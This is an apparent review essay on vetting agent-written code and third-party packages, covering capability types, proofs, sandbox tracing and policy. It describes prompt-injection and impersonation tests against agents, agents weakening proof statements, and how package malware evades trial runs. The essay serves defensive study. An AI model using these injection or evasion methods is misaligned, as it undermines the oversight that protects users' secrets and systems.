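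In 2006, Kevin Hamlen, Greg Morrisett and Schneider compared monitoring with two alternatives, one of which was static analysis. Static analysis can enforce a policy only if some procedure always finishes and correctly separates the programs that comply from those that don't. A monitor requires only that every violation show up after a finite part of a run. In principle, a monitor can also enforce any policy that static analysis can, by running the analysis before the program's first step.

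The other alternative, rewriting, changes a program before it runs so that it complies with a policy. Programs that already complied keep behaving as before. A rewriter can build a monitor's checks into the program, and it can also enforce some policies that monitors can't. In one example, an information-flow policy requires programs to behave as though a secret file did not exist. A rewriter can enforce this by replacing each request for a list of files with one that omits the secret file.

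These results concern what is possible in principle, regardless of the time or computing power required. In practice, a monitor has two drawbacks. It acts after the program has started and perhaps done half its work, and it cannot check code that a given run never reaches.

### Restricting the language

Compilers already reject some harmless programs for the sake of certainty. The Java compiler rejects a program that puts text into a variable meant for numbers, even if that line would never run, and the programmer has to rewrite the line. A language can restrict access to files and networks in the same way.

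*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) applies this idea to AI agents. The paper's system, TACIT, is an open-source server that an agent such as Claude Code can connect to as a tool. The agent sends TACIT a short program in the language Scala 3 instead of calling separate tools to read a file or fetch a page. TACIT runs the program only if the compiler accepts it.

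The method relies on capability tokens, which are program values that code needs in order to use specific resources. To write to a file, for example, code needs the token for that file. Scala's experimental capture checking makes the compiler record in each value's type which tokens that value may use. A function that takes text and writes it to the file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where `Unit` means that it returns no useful value. A function with the type `String -> String`, without braces, holds no tokens and is therefore pure, meaning that it can compute a result but can't write a file, contact a server or print.

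TACIT uses pure functions to protect secrets. When a program reads a file from a folder that the user has marked as classified, it gets the content inside a sealed container. The container's `map` method applies a function to the content and seals the result again, but accepts only pure functions. This simplified program contains one permitted use and one leak:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
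  val report = access("/project/report.txt")
  val key = readClassified("/project/secret/key.txt")

  val tidy = key.map(k => k.trim)                  // accepted
  val leak = key.map(k => { report.write(k); k })  // rejected
}
```

The function in the `tidy` line only removes spaces, so it is pure. The one in the `leak` line uses `report`, which gives it the type `String ->{report} String`. That doesn't match the pure type that `map` requires, so the compiler rejects the program and none of it runs.

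The compiler would also reject `report.write("done")` in the same place, although the word "done" reveals nothing about the key. Rice's theorem makes some wrong rejections of this kind unavoidable. The agent can easily fix this one by moving the line outside `map`.

An agent might also try to keep a token for later, for instance by returning a function that still uses it. The compiler rejects this too, because the function's type would have to name a token that exists only inside the block. The agent's access for one step therefore ends with that step.

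The agent can still work with secrets it can't read. It can pass a sealed document to a separate, trusted language model on the user's own machine and get back a sealed summary. If the agent prints the summary, the user sees the text on a separate channel and the agent receives only `Classified(****)`.

### Safe mode and what TACIT trusts

Ordinary Scala lets code bypass its type system, so TACIT compiles agents' code in a restricted "safe mode". This mode bans type casts and pattern matches that the compiler can't check, the library's explicitly unsafe features, annotations that switch off checks, and run-time reflection. It also turns on capture checking, including tracking changes to data, and a stricter treatment of missing values. Code can use global objects and functions only if they are safe, which rules out the standard print functions.

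Safe mode can't ban exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, because even dividing by zero can cause one. An exception could carry a secret out of a pure function, so TACIT catches exceptions while the program runs and turns them into ordinary values, which it can seal.

The guarantee depends on four trusted components: the Scala compiler, TACIT's library, the runtime that executes the code and, if the user has one, the local language model. Library developers can also mark a module as safe to exempt it from the restrictions, but they must then verify it themselves. Odersky and colleagues treat everything else as potentially hostile, including the agent's own model. Computer-checked proofs exist for the basic type system, but none yet shows that safe mode provides all its intended guarantees.

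TACIT also makes some checks only while a program is running. It stops a program that tries to open a file outside the folder it requested or contact a server outside its list. In the published examples, the agent's own code names the folder, servers or commands it requests, so a gate would still need a policy on which requests to grant.

### How TACIT did in tests

In the main safety test, agents worked on a sample project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. The test paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, some of which included ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. In another 11 tasks, the user asked for secrets directly or posed as someone with authority, such as an administrator in an emergency. Each model did all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets sealed and once with them in plain text.

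| Model | Leaks, sealed | Leaks, plain text | Ordinary tasks completed, sealed | Ordinary tasks completed, plain text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0 of 131 | 2 of 131 | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 0 of 131 | 11 of 131 | 90.0% | 88.3% |

The difference comes mostly from malicious users. MiniMax leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 malicious tasks but in only 3 of the 120 injection trials, and Sonnet resisted every injection without help from types. The trials also used a fixed set of ten injections. The type-system argument is therefore better evidence of protection against a determined attacker than the count of zero leaks. Sonnet's lower completion rate with plain text may be an artefact, since it often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

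The researchers also used AgentDojo, an existing set of prompt-injection tests covering banking, office work, Slack and travel. Across two models, the attack was counted as successful in 1 of 1,926 trials. In that trial, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another one. The policy allowed the agent to quote those reviews.

Odersky and colleagues compare TACIT on the same tests with CaMeL, a system that tracks sensitive data while a program runs. They describe the two systems' completion rates as comparable, but some of the rates differ widely. With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks and CaMeL completed 81%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64% of the travel tasks and CaMeL completed 1%.

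Writing typed Scala did not make the agents noticeably worse at their work. On simulated customer service, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls. They had to resubmit at most 8% of their programs after a compiler error. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, a difference of about five issues. This test is the closest to a coding agent's work, but it covered only one model.

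### Code outside the restricted language

The issues in SWE-bench Lite come from Python projects. TACIT checked the Scala programs the agent used to read and edit files, but not the Python it wrote into those files. In the invoice example, TACIT could limit what the agent does while building the page. It would not check the page itself or the PDF library if they are written in Python or JavaScript.

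The gap matters as soon as the agent runs the project's tests, because they start as a separate process. Odersky and colleagues note that the guarantee then covers only which commands the agent may run. They advise allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and Scala's build tool `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. Even `sbt` is risky for an agent that can edit the project, because `sbt` executes the project's build file, where the agent could put any code.

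According to Odersky and colleagues, Scala 3 is the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types. Other mainstream languages would need to add this tracking and ban features that bypass it. Such restrictions can be severe in Python. CaMeL's agents write in a subset of the language that has no recursion or user-defined functions, which would exclude practically every package on PyPI.

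The approach suits short scripts that an agent writes for a single task, because the host program can choose the language. The shared part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines of Scala, each new application area needs perhaps a few hundred more, and checking a typical script takes less than a second. The checks don't make a script correct. A script that passes could still delete the wrong invoices in a folder it is allowed to write to, or leak a secret slowly through timing, for example by taking longer when a digit is a 7.

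### Asking the producer for a proof

A gate can accept code in other languages if someone else supplies a proof that the code is safe. Rice's theorem rules out a general method for deciding whether code is safe, but someone may still find a proof for a particular program, and checking a finished proof is a mechanical task that always ends.

George Necula and Peter Lee turned this into a method in 1996, called proof-carrying code. It works as follows:

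1. The consumer, who will run the code, publishes a safety policy.
2. The producer writes the code and a formal proof that it obeys the policy.
3. The consumer's software works out from the code itself a logical formula that, if true, guarantees that the code obeys the policy.
4. A small checker confirms that the proof establishes exactly this formula, and the consumer then runs the code.

Suppose the policy is that code may read only inside a block of memory with `len` bytes, and the code reads positions 0 to n − 1. For this code, the formula would be roughly

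for every i, if 0 ≤ i < n and n ≤ len, then 0 ≤ i < len

which is easy to prove. The policy also has to guarantee that n ≤ len when the code starts. If it doesn't, the producer has to add a test to the code.

The consumer doesn't need to trust the producer, and a signature wouldn't strengthen the guarantee. If an attacker changes the code in transit, the formula changes too. Either the old proof no longer fits and the checker rejects it, or the proof still fits and the changed code also obeys the policy. Necula and Lee tried this with small programs that sort network traffic inside an operating system's kernel. Checking a proof took 1 to 3 milliseconds, and the programs needed no further checks as they ran.

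Writing the proofs was the main difficulty, and language models have changed that. In *Prediction*, Kleppmann (2025) argues that writing proofs is one of the best uses for these models, because made-up proofs do no harm. The checker rejects an invalid proof, and the model tries again. For the same reason, a coding agent can be allowed to write the proof for its own code. The blog post *log who watches the watchers* describes how ten agents wrote a version of the compression library zlib, together with proofs about it, in the proof language Lean.

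### Proofs for 123 existing libraries

In October 2026, Anthropic and the start-up Theorem published proofs about software already in use. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries and, in the process, found bugs that had gone undetected for years.

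The project started from existing fuzz tests, which are small programs that feed a library huge numbers of generated inputs to see whether it crashes. All 123 libraries belong to OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that runs such tests for open-source software. The number of different inputs just under 64 megabytes has more than 150 million digits. A proof covers all of them, while a fuzz test can try only a tiny fraction.

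EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports proofs that the compiled code of each of 239 test programs exits normally on every input under 64 megabytes, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion (a check that the programmer wrote into the code). Claude wrote the proofs for the proof system Rocq. They were checked by Rocq's kernel, the small part that everything else in the system relies on. The work took a few weeks.

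The guarantee has several bounds:

- It covers the functions that the test programs use, and the libraries may have bugs elsewhere.
- Each program runs as a single thread, with all its libraries built in and a fixed amount of memory.
- The programs run on RISC-V, a type of processor, and on a mathematical model of Linux.
- Claude patched some of the bugs it found, and in those cases the proof applies to the patched code.

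The processor matters because most laptops and servers use x86 or ARM chips, and a proof about the RISC-V version would not catch a mistake that a compiler made only in the x86 version. Work on these more common processors has begun. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presents what the security firm Zellic believes to be the first published proof that covers a complete x86 Linux program of a common kind. In *AlphaProof Code* (2026), Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues at Google prove properties of the ARM machine code of the library behind the messaging app Signal, without changing the library. Proofs about machine code do not require anyone to trust the compiler.

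These proofs are too long for anyone to read. *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) puts the Rocq code that Claude wrote for the 123 libraries at a billion lines. People don't need to read the proofs if the checker is sound, but they do have to examine the statement of what each proof establishes and the model of the machine. In the Signal project, about 6.5 million lines of proof depend on about 26,000 lines of such trusted material, which is still a lot for a reviewer to read.

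The more serious limit for a gate is the property being proved. A library that exits normally without a memory error can still read a publishing token and send it to an attacker. The proofs address vulnerabilities rather than malicious behavior, so they would be little help against a poisoned dependency.

### A proof covers only what someone wrote down

The missing access check on the invoice page is what programmers call a logic bug. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) defines these as conflicts with the implicit rules for how software should work, and notes that they rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect. The page doesn't crash when it shows a customer someone else's invoice. To prove that this never happens, someone first has to write the rule down:

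for every customer c and invoice v, if the page shows v to c, then c owns v

Even this short rule may be wrong, since it omits the company's accountants, who presumably need to see every invoice. The proof checker can't detect such an omission.

*The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) distinguishes two questions that a checker leaves open. Tolmach and Klaus work at Runtime Verification, which sells verification services, so they have an interest in showing that verification needs experts, but they support the point with examples.

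If an agent reads JavaScript and writes its own description of it in Lean, any proof is about the description, and it applies to the JavaScript only if the two match. In one benchmark, researchers asked Claude to model how the database etcd keeps its copies in agreement, and it essentially reproduced the model in the appendix of a well-known paper. The result passed every check but had little to do with etcd's code. Across the benchmark, descriptions written by AI models scored nearly 100% on syntax and about 46% on agreement with the real code. Proofs about machine code largely avoid this problem because they start from the program itself, though they still need an accurate model of the processor.

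A proved property may also fail to match what people want. Researchers gave a language model the deliberately false step that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51 (the right answer is 45). The model wrote this as a formal statement in which x had to be a whole number. No whole number satisfies 3^x = 5, and anything follows from an impossible assumption, so the false step became provable. An agent could similarly "prove" that the invoice page is safe by assuming that the database has no invoices.

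Such errors are common. Tolmach and Klaus cite a study in which 89.5% of an agent's formal statements compiled but only 60.5% were faithful to the original. In another study, language models reviewing specifications missed a quarter of the faulty ones. Tolmach and Klaus also warn that an agent rewarded for completing proofs has an incentive to weaken the statement instead of finding the bug.

Proof-carrying code deals with part of this problem by having the consumer set the policy, so a producer can't choose an easier one. Similarly, the Signal project's checker accepts proofs only against a specification that people have approved. The Anthropic project took its properties from existing tests. A gate for coding agents should protect the property from the agent, just as it should protect a saved capability list.

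The length of a specification also depends on the property to be proved. A full description of what the invoice page should do might be longer than the page's code. A rule such as "opens no network connection and starts no other program" takes one line and could apply to thousands of libraries without anyone describing what each one is for. Such rules seem more practical for a gate to enforce than full correctness, but there appear to be no large collections of proofs that npm or PyPI packages satisfy them. Producing those proofs would require a precise model of JavaScript or Python and of the software that runs it, including the features that let a program generate and execute code while it runs.

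## Trial runs in a sandbox

Hardly any npm or PyPI packages come with a proof, but a gate can run most of them in a sandbox, an isolated environment where they can do little damage, and record what they do. A trial run avoids some of the problems of reading code. If a package unpacks a hidden payload or assembles a function's name from fragments, the record shows what the payload or function did.

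However, the record covers only that run, so malware that stays inactive in the sandbox looks just like harmless code. The published tests below all use third-party packages, mostly from PyPI, and none uses agent-written code.

### What a trial run records

The sandbox is usually a container or a virtual machine with no real credentials. *Preflight* (Jandali, Sheybani and colleagues, 2026) describes a fairly typical one for Python packages. The package runs in a Docker container as an ordinary user, can't gain further privileges or change the system's main files, and has limited resources. A container shares the host's kernel, the core of the operating system, so a flaw in the kernel could let malware escape. *Preflight* suggests small, disposable virtual machines as a stronger alternative.

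To open a file, contact a server or start another program, code has to ask the kernel, and each request is a system call. Tools such as strace log these calls. A simplified, invented log for a new version of the PDF library might look like this:

```
openat("/project/invoice.pdf", write)   ok
connect("fonts.example", port 443)      ok
execve("/usr/bin/curl")                 ok
```

The library wrote the invoice, contacted a server and started the download program `curl`. This kind of tracing works for any programming language, including compiled code, which makes it useful against attacks like the one on October 21, 2026. That day, the release pipeline of LiteLLM, a Python library for using language models from many companies, published a version containing compiled malware. LiteLLM (2026) reports that the pipeline also signed the release.

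Monitoring system calls can miss malware that reads a token from an environment variable. The operating system copies these variables into a program's memory when the program starts, so reading them there doesn't require a system call.

A sinkhole takes the place of the internet. When the package looks up a server's address, the sinkhole returns its own, so the connection never reaches the real server, but the log shows which host the package tried to reach. Without a sinkhole, a trial run can leak real data. In a demonstration in *Pack-A-Mal* (Vu, Nguyen and colleagues, 2025), the attacker's server received an SSH key from the sandbox during the analysis. But a sinkhole also stops malware from downloading its harmful part from a server, so the trial run may record only the attempt.

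The sandbox also compares the file system before and after the run to find lasting changes, such as a new start-up file.

The raw logs contain temporary file names and process numbers that differ from run to run. To make runs comparable, Preflight reduces the logs to a behavioural fingerprint, which is a normalized list of the hosts contacted, sensitive environment variables read, lasting file changes, programs started and types of system call.

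### How Preflight tests a package for one program

Malicious code may run only when a program calls a particular function. A trial run therefore has to call functions as well as install the package, but a large library may have thousands of them. Preflight, published in November 2026, calls only the ones that the user's own program refers to:

1. It reads the program's source code and lists the packages it imports and the functions and classes it uses from each. It rejects any package without an exact version number.
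2. A language model, GPT-5.4 mini, gets this list and some of the package's source code, and writes a harness, a short test program that uses everything on the list.
3. An ordinary program checks that the harness is valid Python, has at most 100 lines, imports the package and calls every function on the list. If the harness fails, the model gets the reason and one chance to revise it. After that, Preflight can fall back on a harness made without a model.
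4. Preflight installs the package in the sandbox, runs the harness and traces both stages.
5. It reduces the traces to a fingerprint, and does the same for an earlier version if there is a suitable one.

Because the model only writes the harness, a malicious package can't cause it to change the sandbox's settings or misread the traces. An attacker might still plant text in the source code that leads the model to call a function with arguments that keep the malware inactive, and the checks on the harness would probably not catch this.

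Preflight then compares the two fingerprints:

new behaviour = F(new version, program) − F(baseline, program)

F is the set of things the package did when the harness used it as the program does. The minus sign removes everything the baseline also did. If the old PDF library only wrote the invoice, the new behaviour in the log above would be contacting `fonts.example` and starting `curl`.

Some new behaviour counts as a critical finding, such as contacting a new host, reading a credential, leaving a file behind or starting a new program. The verdict is "clean" with no critical findings, "suspicious" with one and "malicious" with two or more, though a critical result from a static scanner can override this. The PDF library could therefore get a "malicious" verdict for downloading a font. The comparison can also miss stolen data sent to a host that the baseline already contacted.

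Preflight records the verdict in a signed certificate, along with hashes of the program and of the file listing its dependencies' versions. A separate checker allows the program to run only if the certificate is valid and recent, both hashes match, and the verdict is clean. This prevents an agent from getting a certificate for one program and using it for another. The agent therefore also needs a new certificate each time it edits the program, which could slow down a task with many revisions.

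### Results on four real attacks

Jandali and colleagues tested Preflight on malicious releases of four packages. LiteLLM appears twice because it has two main uses, as a client that sends a program's requests to a language model and as a proxy server that passes on requests from other programs.

| Package | What the program used | Critical findings | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| LiteLLM 1.82.7 | Client functions | 0 | Clean |
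| LiteLLM 1.82.7 | Proxy server | 14 | Malicious |
| Ultralytics 8.3.41 | Constructor for an image-recognition model | 6 | Malicious |
| ctx 0.2.2 | Constructor for the package's main object | 3 | Malicious |
| DurableTask | Not compared with an earlier version | 3 | Malicious |

All five verdicts come from the fixed rule, and static scanners didn't decide any of them. The researchers had also planned to let a larger language model weigh the evidence, but its input was too long in every case.

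Ultralytics is the most convincing result. The malicious version contacted a new endpoint and started a new program, the two behaviors the researchers had predicted. Three of the six findings are different paths to `curl`, so less happened than the count suggests, but the new endpoint and program are enough for the verdict.

DurableTask is the weakest case. One of its three critical findings was a connection to a suspicious domain, but the other two came from the sandbox's own sinkhole and Docker's address service. Without those two, the rule gives "suspicious" instead of "malicious". The checker would still have blocked the package, since it accepts only clean verdicts, but a system that treats the two verdicts differently would need a corrected count. The trial run also recorded neither of the behaviours the researchers expected, a lasting file change and a new program. The package's source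 code contains a downloader, but with the sinkhole in place there was no sign that it received and ran a payload.

The ctx verdict may have a similar problem. All three findings were network endpoints, but Jandali and colleagues describe only one endpoint that the earlier version didn't contact. If the earlier version made no connections, the sinkhole and the address service would also look new in this comparison. They don't identify the three endpoints, so this is only a possibility.

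The traces of ctx and the LiteLLM proxy should also have shown reads of environment variables, but they contain none. This may be because reading an environment variable doesn't require a system call.

The proxy test was exploratory. The preregistered test used LiteLLM as a client and never reached the malicious code. The proxy result shows that Preflight can detect the malware when a program runs it, but gives little idea of how often a program chosen without knowledge of the attack would run it.

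### What the clean LiteLLM verdict covers

The clean verdict was correct for a program that uses only LiteLLM's client. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) reports that the malicious code in version 1.82.7 was in `proxy_server.py`. Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM* explains that the code ran when other code imported `litellm.proxy`, which an ordinary client program wouldn't do.

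The attackers published version 1.82.8 13 minutes later. It kept the code in `proxy_server.py` and added a new file, `litellm_init.pth`. Python can run code from files of this type when it starts. According to a bug report quoted on the Openwall mailing list, the file contained a script that stole credentials every time Python started, whether or not a program imported LiteLLM. Version 1.82.8 was therefore unsafe even for the client program that had been safe with 1.82.7.

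PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) says that the malware "ran on install" and doesn't distinguish between the two releases. According to Willison's *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8* (2026), installing 1.82.8 was enough to trigger the malware, while 1.82.7 had to be imported.

Jandali and colleagues didn't test 1.82.8. Preflight would probably have detected it whatever program it was testing, because Preflight has to start Python in the sandbox to run the harness. A certificate for 1.82.7 wouldn't have allowed 1.82.8, since the version number had changed. Even 1.82.7 was dangerous on a machine where a second program ran the proxy from the same installation, so the clean verdict doesn't show that LiteLLM is safe as long as programs use only the client.

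LiteLLM's developers used similar reasoning in May 2026, when attackers published a malicious version of `mistralai`, a package for using Mistral's models. The malware ran when a program imported the package, and the developers told users they were not affected because LiteLLM never imports it. LiteLLM also doesn't install the package, a reason that would hold even against a file like `litellm_init.pth`.

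### Harmless packages and merely importing the code

Preflight gave a clean verdict to all 100 harmless packages in a separate test. If its true false-positive rate is p, the chance of getting no false positives in 100 independent tests is

(1 − p)^100

This equals 5% when p is about 3%, so at 95% confidence the true rate could still be as high as about 3%. The calculation also treats the packages as a random sample, but the researchers selected them from packages related to AI and data work.

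They also don't report how many of the 100 had an earlier version for comparison. Without a baseline, Preflight counts everything a package does as new. In the DurableTask test, this included connections to the sandbox's own addresses. A harmless package that contacts a server might get the same two spurious findings. The test is also less informative about updates that add features, where most false alarms would presumably occur.

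In another experiment, Jandali and colleagues replaced the harnesses for Ultralytics and ctx with ones that only imported the package, and changed nothing else. Both malicious packages now got a clean verdict, though they had been flagged as malicious with the original harnesses. A trial run that only installs and imports a package can therefore miss malware that a single ordinary function call would trigger.

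Two cases are too few to estimate how often this happens. The experiment also doesn't show that a language model is needed to write the harness, because the researchers didn't compare the model with an ordinary program that had the same information about which functions to call.

### Judging a package for all its users

A registry can't test each package with every program that might use it. Systems for registries therefore test each package as a whole. Package Analysis, a project of the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), runs packages from npm, PyPI and other registries inside nested containers. It installs, imports and then executes each package, and records the commands, files and network addresses involved.

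*PyFEX* (Wang, Fan and colleagues, 2026) gave its traces to GPT-5 and asked whether each package was malicious. The test set had equal numbers of malicious and harmless packages. With the traces alone, GPT-5 caught 45.2% of the malicious packages, and only half of the packages it flagged were malicious, so it did no better than guessing. When it also had evidence from static analysis, it caught 83.8% of the malicious packages, and 93.6% of the packages it flagged were malicious.

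This probably makes trial runs look worse than they would be for new packages. The malware was old, and only 29 of the attackers' servers in the data were still accessible. Malware that couldn't reach its server may have crashed before doing anything recognisable. A new package would be more likely to reach its server, unless the sandbox used a sinkhole.

In *DySec*, Mehedi, Islam and colleagues (2025) got much better results with a trained classifier. They installed 14,271 PyPI packages, about half of them malicious, on 16 Raspberry Pi computers. Small monitoring programs in the Linux kernel recorded file access, network connections and system calls. The classifier used 36 measurements from these records, such as how often a package opened files in protected folders.

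It classified 96.0% of the test packages correctly. The best classifier that used only static features reached 95.3%, so tracing added little to the overall accuracy. DySec did better on 500 malicious packages from a later collection. It missed 19 of them, compared with 70 for the best static classifier. (The paper's claim of 78.65% fewer misses matches a comparison with a weaker static classifier that missed 89. Against the best one, the reduction is 73%.)

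*QUT-DV25* (Mehedi, Jurdak and colleagues, 2025), the companion paper that presents the dataset, gives a false-positive rate of 3.23% for the same classifier. At PyPI's volume of roughly 2,485 releases a day, that would mean about 80 false alarms daily.

The classifier may also have learned to recognise broken packages. During installation, 161 of the malicious packages and none of the harmless ones were found to lack their setup files. One of the strongest signs of malware was an attempt to open a file that didn't exist. Such signs could be less useful against an attacker who adds a few malicious lines to a popular, working package.

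DySec flagged 11 PyPI packages that were supposedly harmless. The researchers judged six of them malicious and reported them to PyPI, which removed four. PyPI's maintainers defended the other two, including PySocks, whose purpose is to relay network traffic. The trace accurately recorded what the package did, but it could not show whether the intent was malicious.

### How often malware waits or checks its surroundings

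Wang and colleagues studied how malware avoids detection in 2,961 malicious PyPI packages. They started with 10,920 packages and removed near-duplicates and harmless ones. A package can appear in several rows of this table. The shares were calculated from the counts because two of the published percentages don't match them.

| Behaviour | Packages | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Runs during installation or import | 2,408 | 81.3% |
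| Looks for particular programs or files | 664 | 22.4% |
| Runs only after a specific call | 564 | 19.0% |
| Checks the operating system | 486 | 16.4% |
| Waits before acting | 345 | 11.7% |
| Checks the network | 218 | 7.4% |
| Looks for debugging tools | 206 | 7.0% |
| Looks for signs of a sandbox | 184 | 6.2% |

Overall, 59% of the packages checked the environment they were running in or hid code where an ordinary trial run was unlikely to reach it. Some of these checks may have had another purpose. For example, a program written to steal passwords from Windows has to check whether it is running on Windows.

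A trial run that only installs and imports packages would still trigger most of the malware. Ryan, Ifti and colleagues (2025) found a similar pattern in *Unveiling Malicious Logic*, for which they read 370 malicious Python packages line by line. Of the malicious features they marked, 86% were in `setup.py`, which can run during installation.

As in the npm study, both samples contain only malware that someone had already caught, so they probably over-represent code that runs during installation. They also include many packages that were malicious from the start. An attacker who takes over a popular package can instead hide code in a function that its users already call, as in the Ultralytics attack.

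A longer trial run might help detect malware that waits before acting. Mehedi and colleagues watched 64 high-risk packages for between one and ten minutes and saw nothing new after two, so they used two minutes for the whole dataset. Vu and colleagues give the default in Package Analysis as 10 seconds, which leaves much less time for delayed behaviour to appear. But malware could wait for a day or until a certain date, and even a ten-minute test would miss that. The two-minute limit is a practical compromise, and attackers who know about it could design malware to wait longer.

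DySec's computers all ran Linux, and the researchers acknowledge that they may have missed attacks that start only on Windows or macOS, or only after a user does something.

### Running both sides of every branch

It is hard to build a sandbox that looks exactly like a real user's computer. Wang and colleagues' system, PyFEX, deals with this by running code even when its conditions aren't met. Suppose a package contains these lines:

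```python
if today == "Monday":
    contact_server()
save_report()
```

On a Wednesday, an ordinary trial run would record only the saved report. PyFEX uses a modified version of Python that splits the run into two processes at the `if`. One process skips the call to the server, as an ordinary run would, and the other makes it.

Ten such conditions in a row would give 2^10 = 1,024 paths. To limit this growth, PyFEX merges the two processes when the branches meet again, here at `save_report()`, and keeps the record of what each one did. On the 2,961 malicious packages, it used 44 processes on average, compared with 955 in a simulation without merging.

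A forced branch often crashes because it needs something that isn't there, such as a reply from an offline server. PyFEX then supplies a placeholder that accepts any operation and records where it came from. If a package tries to read a missing password file and send its contents away, the log shows that the outgoing data would have come from that file.

After the main run, PyFEX also calls every function that hasn't run yet. This step had the largest effect, increasing executed statements by 47%. In packages with evasive checks, running both branches exposed about 20 more statements on average. Recovering from crashes exposed about 93 more in packages that would otherwise have stopped.

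A language model, GPT-4.1 mini, then reads the log and decides whether the package is malicious. In the researchers' main test, the system caught 99.9% of the malicious packages with a precision of 99.1%. These figures are probably somewhat too high, because the researchers had corrected the dataset after reviewing cases where their system disagreed with its labels. The dataset's maintainers confirmed the corrections, but this method would miss wrong labels that the system agreed with.

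A test on new uploads is better evidence. Over 90 days from August 1, 2025, the system analysed 50,427 packages from PyPI and flagged 222. Of these, 212 were previously unknown malicious packages, which PyPI's security team confirmed. The other 10 were false positives, about 0.02% of the harmless packages, or roughly one false alarm every two days at PyPI's full volume. In eight of them, the language model gave a correct explanation but still answered "malicious".

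The test can't show how many malicious packages the system missed. PyPI removed some packages that the system had passed, including tools that try long lists of names to find out which accounts exist on a service. PyFEX had recorded these tools' requests, but the language model didn't classify them as malicious.

Forced execution can also show behaviour that would never happen in normal use. For example, PyFEX ran sample attacks from security-testing libraries, which a user would have to call deliberately. PyFEX can't reveal an encrypted payload without the key, and it can't trace execution inside compiled C or C++ modules. System-call tracing can record what such a module does, but only on the path the module takes during that run, so it could be useful to run both.

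### Time and cost

| System | Time per package | Reported cost |
|---|---|---|
| OpenSSF Package Analysis | 10 seconds by default | None given |
| DySec | 120 seconds | None given |
| PyFEX | 75 seconds on average | None given |
| Preflight | None given | About $0.003 per harness |

The delay of less than half a second in DySec's abstract is the time the classifier took to judge the whole test set once the traces were ready. Preflight's cost of $0.027 for nine harnesses covers only the language model that wrote them, not the computing time for the sandbox.

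These times would be manageable for a registry. At two minutes each, PyPI's 2,485 daily releases would take about 83 hours of machine time, which four computers could just about handle in a day. A developer waiting for an agent would notice the delay more. If a request brought in 79 new packages, as in the earlier npm estimate, running them one after another at PyFEX's speed would take about 99 minutes.

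Testing packages in parallel would help, and so would saving the results. Once someone has tested a package as a whole, everyone who installs the same file can use the verdict. Preflight's verdicts are harder to share because each one applies to a single program. A company could use shared verdicts for most packages and program-specific tests for those with access to something valuable.

### Trial runs of an agent's own code

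The previous commit could be the baseline for code that an agent writes. The gate would run the same tests on the old and new versions of the program in a sandbox and compare their behavior. Agents usually test their code anyway, so this might add little time. Nobody appears to have measured how well this comparison works.

A trial run should be good at catching mistakes with visible effects. If the agent's clean-up script deletes the wrong directory, the file comparison would show this, provided the sandbox has a copy of the directory. The missing access check on the invoice page is harder to catch, because the page's fingerprint would match that of a correct page. To find it, a test would have to log in as one customer and ask for another customer's invoice.

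An agent that left out the access check when writing the page may also leave out the test for it. It could also write tests that never reach a harmful part of the code, either by accident or because it followed a planted instruction. A person or a different model would therefore need to choose at least some of the tests. Preflight's division of work could be adapted for this, with a separate model writing the tests and an ordinary program checking whether they call every function the agent changed.

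## Turning findings into a decision

A trial run may record that the PDF library contacted `fonts.example`, but someone has to decide beforehand whether the library is allowed to do that and write the decision into the policy. Even with accurate evidence, a gate can pass or block the wrong code if its rules are too coarse, and people may switch it off if the rules are too strict.

### What a policy has to fix

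"Be careful with network access" is too vague for a gate to apply. A workable rule has to fix five things:

- the subject, which is the artifact or group of artifacts that the rule covers
- the capability, such as reading files or using the network
- the resource, such as one folder or one host
- the context, such as a developer's laptop or a build server
- the default, which applies when evidence is missing or no rule fits

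The rule that limits document libraries to the project folder, for example, still lacks a context and a default.

*From Agent Output to Authorized Transition* (Koch, 2026) proposes further conditions for verdicts on agents' work. The paper is a design and reports no results from real use. Koch would tie each verdict to the exact artifact and policy version, so a pass under an old version of the policy wouldn't count under a new one. Koch also limits what each kind of evidence can establish, so a unit test, for example, can't show that a person approved a release.

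Findings can also conflict. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, present FORGE, a monitor that checks an agent's actions before they take effect. Its verdict on an action *a* follows a fixed order:

1. If any rule denies *a*, block it.
2. If no rule denies *a* and at least one allows it, allow it.
3. If no rule applies, use the default.

If a package gate worked this way, a clean static scan could never cancel out a password theft recorded during a trial run.

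Missing evidence is easy to overlook because programs often keep running without it. According to Anthropic's documentation, if Claude Code's sandbox can't start, Claude Code by default shows a warning and runs commands without it. Administrators who rely on the sandbox have to change a setting to make this a failure. Missing evidence can also let an action pass a rule by accident. For example, an upload with no recorded destination satisfies "every destination must be on the approved list" because there is no destination to check. FORGE has a separate rule that denies the action if the destination field is empty and the agent has read untrusted content.

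A strict default has a cost too, because a broken scanner can then stop everyone's work.

### Verdicts between allow and block

Brett Smith of the software company SAS, quoted by ReversingLabs, recommends moving toward a "binary authorization policy". A policy that can only allow or block is simple to apply, but it suits new packages poorly. Blocking the download prevents anyone from examining the package, while allowing it without limits may let an install script run with the developer's credentials before anyone has looked at it.

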